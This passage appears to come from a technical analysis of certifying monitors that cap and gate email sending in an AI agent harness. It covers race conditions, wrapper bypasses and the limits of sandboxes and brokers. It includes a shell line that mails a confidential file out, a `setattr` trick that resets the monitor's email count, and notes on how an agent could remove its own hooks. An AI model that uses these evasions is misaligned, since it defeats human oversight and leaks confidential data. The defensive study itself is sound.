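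Finally, the certifier scans the rest of the harness. No other code may write to `secret` or `sent`, or call `do_read`, `do_shell` or `do_send`.

Some of the earlier methods would reject even this correct wrapper. The ActionScript certifier doesn't support updates before an event, or events that depend on a run-time argument. Mobile would require the wrapper to keep its state in packages, and its prototype has no events that concern a whole run. Cheko's constraint lists and Dam and Lundblad's shipped proofs both suit the wrapper if it is single-threaded. Someone would still have to adapt them to the harness's language and add the ranges to Cheko's invariant. The verdicts below follow from the published rules of these two methods.

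### Fault one: a read fails after returning data

Suppose a developer moves the update to after the read:

```
text = do_read(path)
if confidential(path): secret = 1
return text
```

This works only if reads succeed. Suppose `do_read` gets halfway through a confidential file on a network drive, loses the connection, and throws an exception whose message includes the text read so far. The second line never runs. The harness catches the exception and adds its message to the conversation so that the model can see what went wrong. The model now has confidential text, but `secret` is still 0, so the guard will allow an email.

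Developers could make the same mistake with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. It supports *hooks*, which are checks that run at set points, such as before or after a tool call. According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, a `PostToolUse` hook runs only if the tool succeeds, but the model still receives a shell command's output when the command fails. A `PostToolUse` hook meant to record confidential reads would therefore miss a command that printed a confidential file and then exited with an error code. Claude Code has a separate event for failures, but it doesn't fire when a user cancels a running tool. Recording the read before the call avoids both problems.

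Cheko's method would reject the faulty wrapper because the exception is another exit from the marked region, and at that exit C is 1 but `secret` is 0, just as with vrenamer's exception handler. This assumes that the certifier's model allows `do_read` to throw an exception. If the model treated reads as always succeeding, the certifier would accept the wrapper.

Dam and Lundblad's checker adds ghost updates before the call, after it, and in a handler that catches anything the call throws. The policy here puts the event at the call, so the checker rejects any wrapper that sets `secret` after the read, because the two monitors must already match when the call begins. If the policy had a rule only for normal returns, the ghost monitor would also miss the failed read, and the faulty wrapper would pass.

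Failed emails raise a similar problem. A mail server may accept a message and then lose the connection, so that `do_send` reports a failure even though the email went out. The wrapper above still counts that email. Agenra also charges for a call before the tool runs and gives no refund if the tool fails. Dyad, an app builder whose message limits Shivakumar and colleagues studied, refunds failed messages. If the email wrapper gave refunds by subtracting 1 from `sent`, N would stay the same, so the invariant would fail and a certifier would reject the code.

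### Fault two: two parallel emails both see a count of nine

Models can request several tools in one reply, and a harness may run them at the same time. Without the lock, this can happen after nine emails:

```
thread 1:  reads sent = 9, passes the guard
thread 2:  reads sent = 9, passes the guard
thread 1:  sets sent = 10, sends the tenth email
thread 2:  sets sent = 10, sends the eleventh email
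```

Claude Code's `PostToolUse` hooks also run at the same time when the model makes parallel calls, so a hook that counts emails needs its own lock. A hook on `PostToolBatch`, which fires once after all the calls in a batch have finished, would give an accurate count, but only after the emails had been sent.

Cheko's method would accept this faulty wrapper because it ignores other threads, so the recipient has to know not to rely on it here. The same applies to the system Dam and Lundblad built in 2010.

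The locking rule proposed for threaded programs would catch the fault. Without the lock, no assertion may mention `sent`, so the certifier can't rule out N = 10 when the email goes out. This assumes that all threads use the same lock and belong to the same process.

Some Python harnesses run tool calls as coroutines instead of threads. Coroutines on a single event loop run one at a time and switch only at an `await`. With no `await` between the guard and the update, two calls can't both read a count of nine. But if a developer later adds an `await` there, perhaps to ask the user for approval, the fault returns. A certifier for such code would have to treat every `await` as a point where other code may change `sent`.

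The policy is also stricter than it needs to be for parallel calls. If a single reply requests both a confidential read and an email, the model wrote the email before it saw the file, so the email can't contain anything from that read. The wrapper still refuses the email if the read runs first. A more precise policy would treat the read event as occurring when the file's contents enter the conversation.

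### Fault three: a tool bypasses the wrapper

Months later, another developer adds a tool that emails a weekly report, and registers it directly with the harness:

```
extra["send_report"] = do_send
...
if tool in extra: return extra[tool](args)
return call(tool, args)
```

The wrapper is still correct, but calls to `send_report` never reach it.

Whether a certifier rejects the harness depends on how the policy defines sending an email. If the policy defines it as using the tool named `send_email`, then using `send_report` isn't an event, and every certifier would accept the harness. The policy here names the underlying function, `do_send`, so Cheko's scan would look for uses of `do_send` outside the wrapper. Dam and Lundblad's checker would add a ghost update before each call to `do_send`, and the proof would fail if there were no guard there. If the new tool used a different mail library,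 the policy would have to list that library's functions too.

The certifier must also determine which function each call runs. The call `extra[tool](args)` picks a function from a table by name at run time, so a sound certifier must either determine everything the table could contain or reject the harness. The wrapper avoids this problem by using a fixed series of `if` statements.

Current products have similar gaps. According to OpenAI's documentation for its agent toolkit, tool guardrails cover functions that developers define as tools, but not hosted tools or the built-in shell, file-patching and computer-control tools. In Claude Code, a developer might use the pattern `mcp__memory` to attach a hook to every tool from a server called `memory`. Anthropic warns that this pattern matches no tools and that the developer has to write `mcp__memory__.*` instead.

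New tools can also appear after certification. The Model Context Protocol lets a server change its set of tools and offer different tools depending on the user's credentials. No certificate can list them all in advance, so the wrapper's last line refuses any unknown tool. To add a tool, someone must decide which events it can cause and certify the harness again.

### Why the model needs no certificate

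Policy adherence covers every possible input, and the model's reply is an input to the harness. The certifier assumes nothing about `tool` or `args`, so the table of facts holds for any reply, including one that an attacker has influenced through prompt injection.

This works only if the harness treats the reply as data. If it ran the reply as code inside its own process, the model could write `sent = 0`.

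The proof also doesn't show that the permitted emails are harmless. An attacker's web page could cause the model to send ten abusive emails before the model reads anything confidential, and the policy would allow all ten. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) compares an agent under a monitor with a reference agent that follows the intended plan under the same monitor. Most of the insecure cases it found involved an injected call that the monitor allowed but the reference agent could not have made.

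### Fixed code and code that the agent writes

The harness's own code changes only when developers release a new version, so they can certify it once per build, and the speed of certification matters little. Hamlen and colleagues found 46 potentially relevant instructions in a weather widget with a similar read-and-send policy, and Cheko took about five minutes to certify it.

The build has to include all the source code, libraries and settings that affect the wrapper. Before each start, a trusted launcher can compare a digest of these files with the digest of the certified version.

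Claude Code normally picks up changes to its hook settings while it is running, so an agent that could edit the settings file might remove its own monitor. Administrators can prevent this by defining hooks in managed settings, which a user's or project's settings can't disable. Claude Code also normally lets a tool call go ahead if a hook crashes, times out or can't start, unless the developer has set `onFailure` to `block`. A mistyped file name can therefore turn off a monitor even if its code is correct. A certifier would have to model all these rules to certify a wrapper made of hooks.

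Programs that the agent writes need different treatment. Suppose the agent writes this script to greet a list of customers:

```
for c in customers:
    call("send_email", {address: c.address, text: greeting})
```

If the script runs inside the harness process, it is new code that the build's certificate doesn't cover. The certifier has to check it before it runs and again whenever the agent changes it. This check can be much simpler than the build's, because the guards are already in `call`. The certifier only has to scan the script, as it scanned the rest of the harness, for writes to the monitor's variables and for direct use of the three protected functions. This script passes, and the wrapper will stop it after ten emails however long the list is. Waiting five minutes before every script would be impractical, but checks can be much faster, as they were on Dam and Lundblad's phone.

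In Python, however, a scan like this is hard to make reliable. Code in the same process can normally change another module's variables, and it can construct their names as it runs:

```
setattr(wrapper, "se" + "nt", 0)
```

This line resets the count, although the word `sent` doesn't appear in it. The certifier could reject scripts that use `setattr`, but Python offers many other ways to change the count, including `eval`, a module's internal dictionary, and functions that list the objects in memory. Agenra's Python interface has the same weakness. The build's certificate also has to cover every Python library that the harness loads, since any of them could change the count.

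One solution is to have agents write in a restricted language that lacks these features, so that a program can use only the names the harness gives it. Zhou and colleagues take a similar approach with typed agent programs. The drawback is that agents can no longer use ordinary Python libraries.

Another is to run the scripts in WebAssembly, the bytecode format that replaced Native Client in Chrome. A WebAssembly module can reach the outside only through functions and other resources that its host supplies. The harness would supply `call`, and keep `secret` and `sent` in memory that the module can't access. The module could even be a Python interpreter running a script that rewrites itself, because nothing it rewrites would affect the monitor. Before each run, the harness would need only WebAssembly's standard validation, with no separate check against the email policy. But the software that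 runs WebAssembly would join the trusted computing base, unless someone has verified it, as researchers have done for some other sandboxes.

### The exact guarantee

For a build that a sound certifier has accepted, with every later script either certified or kept outside the process, the guarantee is:

> In every session, whatever the model replies and whatever the tools return, the harness process calls `do_send` at most ten times, and never after calling `do_shell` or calling `do_read` on a path for which `confidential` returned true.

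This limits calls to `do_send`, but one call could send two copies of an email if the mail library automatically retries after a timeout. Dam and Lundblad concede that their treatment of library calls falls short of complete mediation in this sense. In a test by Shivakumar and colleagues, the monitor let a tool carry out a deletion that its registration did not declare. Someone therefore has to check that `do_send` sends one email per call and that `do_read` only reads.

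### What a sandbox adds

A single shell command can contain a whole violation:

```
cat plans.txt | mail someone@example.com
```

The wrapper sets `secret` to 1 and runs the command, which reads the file and emails it. The guarantee still holds, because the harness never called `do_send`.

The wrapper could search commands for words such as `mail`, but a command like `sh job.sh` doesn't show what the script does. Claude Code can filter hooks by shell command, but Anthropic describes this filter as best-effort and recommends its permission system for strict rules. Anthropic also notes that a hook on the file-editing tools doesn't run when a shell command changes a file.

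A sandbox without network access closes this gap, because commands inside it can't send anything. The sandbox must also block their access to the harness's files and memory, or a command could edit the wrapper. The sandbox and the operating system then become part of the trusted computing base.

If the sandbox also contains no confidential files, the policy no longer has to count every shell command as a confidential read. This makes the agent much more useful, because under the original policy even running `date` would prevent it from sending email for the rest of the session.

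### Wrong labels

The function `confidential` may give the wrong answer. Suppose an agent reads `plans.txt`, which is confidential, and then uses the shell to write a summary to `notes.txt`. In a new session, it reads `notes.txt` and emails the contents. Both sessions comply with the policy because nobody has labelled `notes.txt` as confidential.

The harness could delete everything in the sandbox at the end of each session, or treat every file that a command has written as confidential. A safer rule for the policy's author is to treat all files as confidential except those on a public list. If the author forgets an entry, the result is a blocked email instead of a leaked file. But no rule about files covers confidential text that a user pastes into the conversation.

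### What a separate process adds

The guarantee covers one process. If someone starts the harness twice, the two sessions can send a total of twenty emails. Any other program on the computer that has the mail password can send emails without limit.

Both problems become easier to control if the wrapper moves into a small, separate process called a *broker*. Only the broker has the mail password and permission to open the files, so the harness has to go through it for every read and every email. The operating system prevents the harness from changing the broker's memory or using the network to send email directly. The broker can apply one limit across several harnesses, but the broker itself must determine when a session begins, because a harness that could signal a new session could reset the count.

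The broker also removes most of the difficulty with Python. The harness and its libraries can alter themselves without affecting the count. So can plugins, which in Claude Code can include JavaScript functions that run inside the harness's process. The certifier checks only the broker, which developers can write in a language that is easier to analyse.

For the policy in this example, a certified broker would therefore be a better choice than a certified wrapper inside a Python harness. However, the broker can check only the requests that reach it, so it could not enforce the more precise rule from fault two, which depends on when a file's contents enter the conversation. That happens inside the harness, so enforcing the rule would require an inlined monitor there and a certifier that can handle the harness's code.
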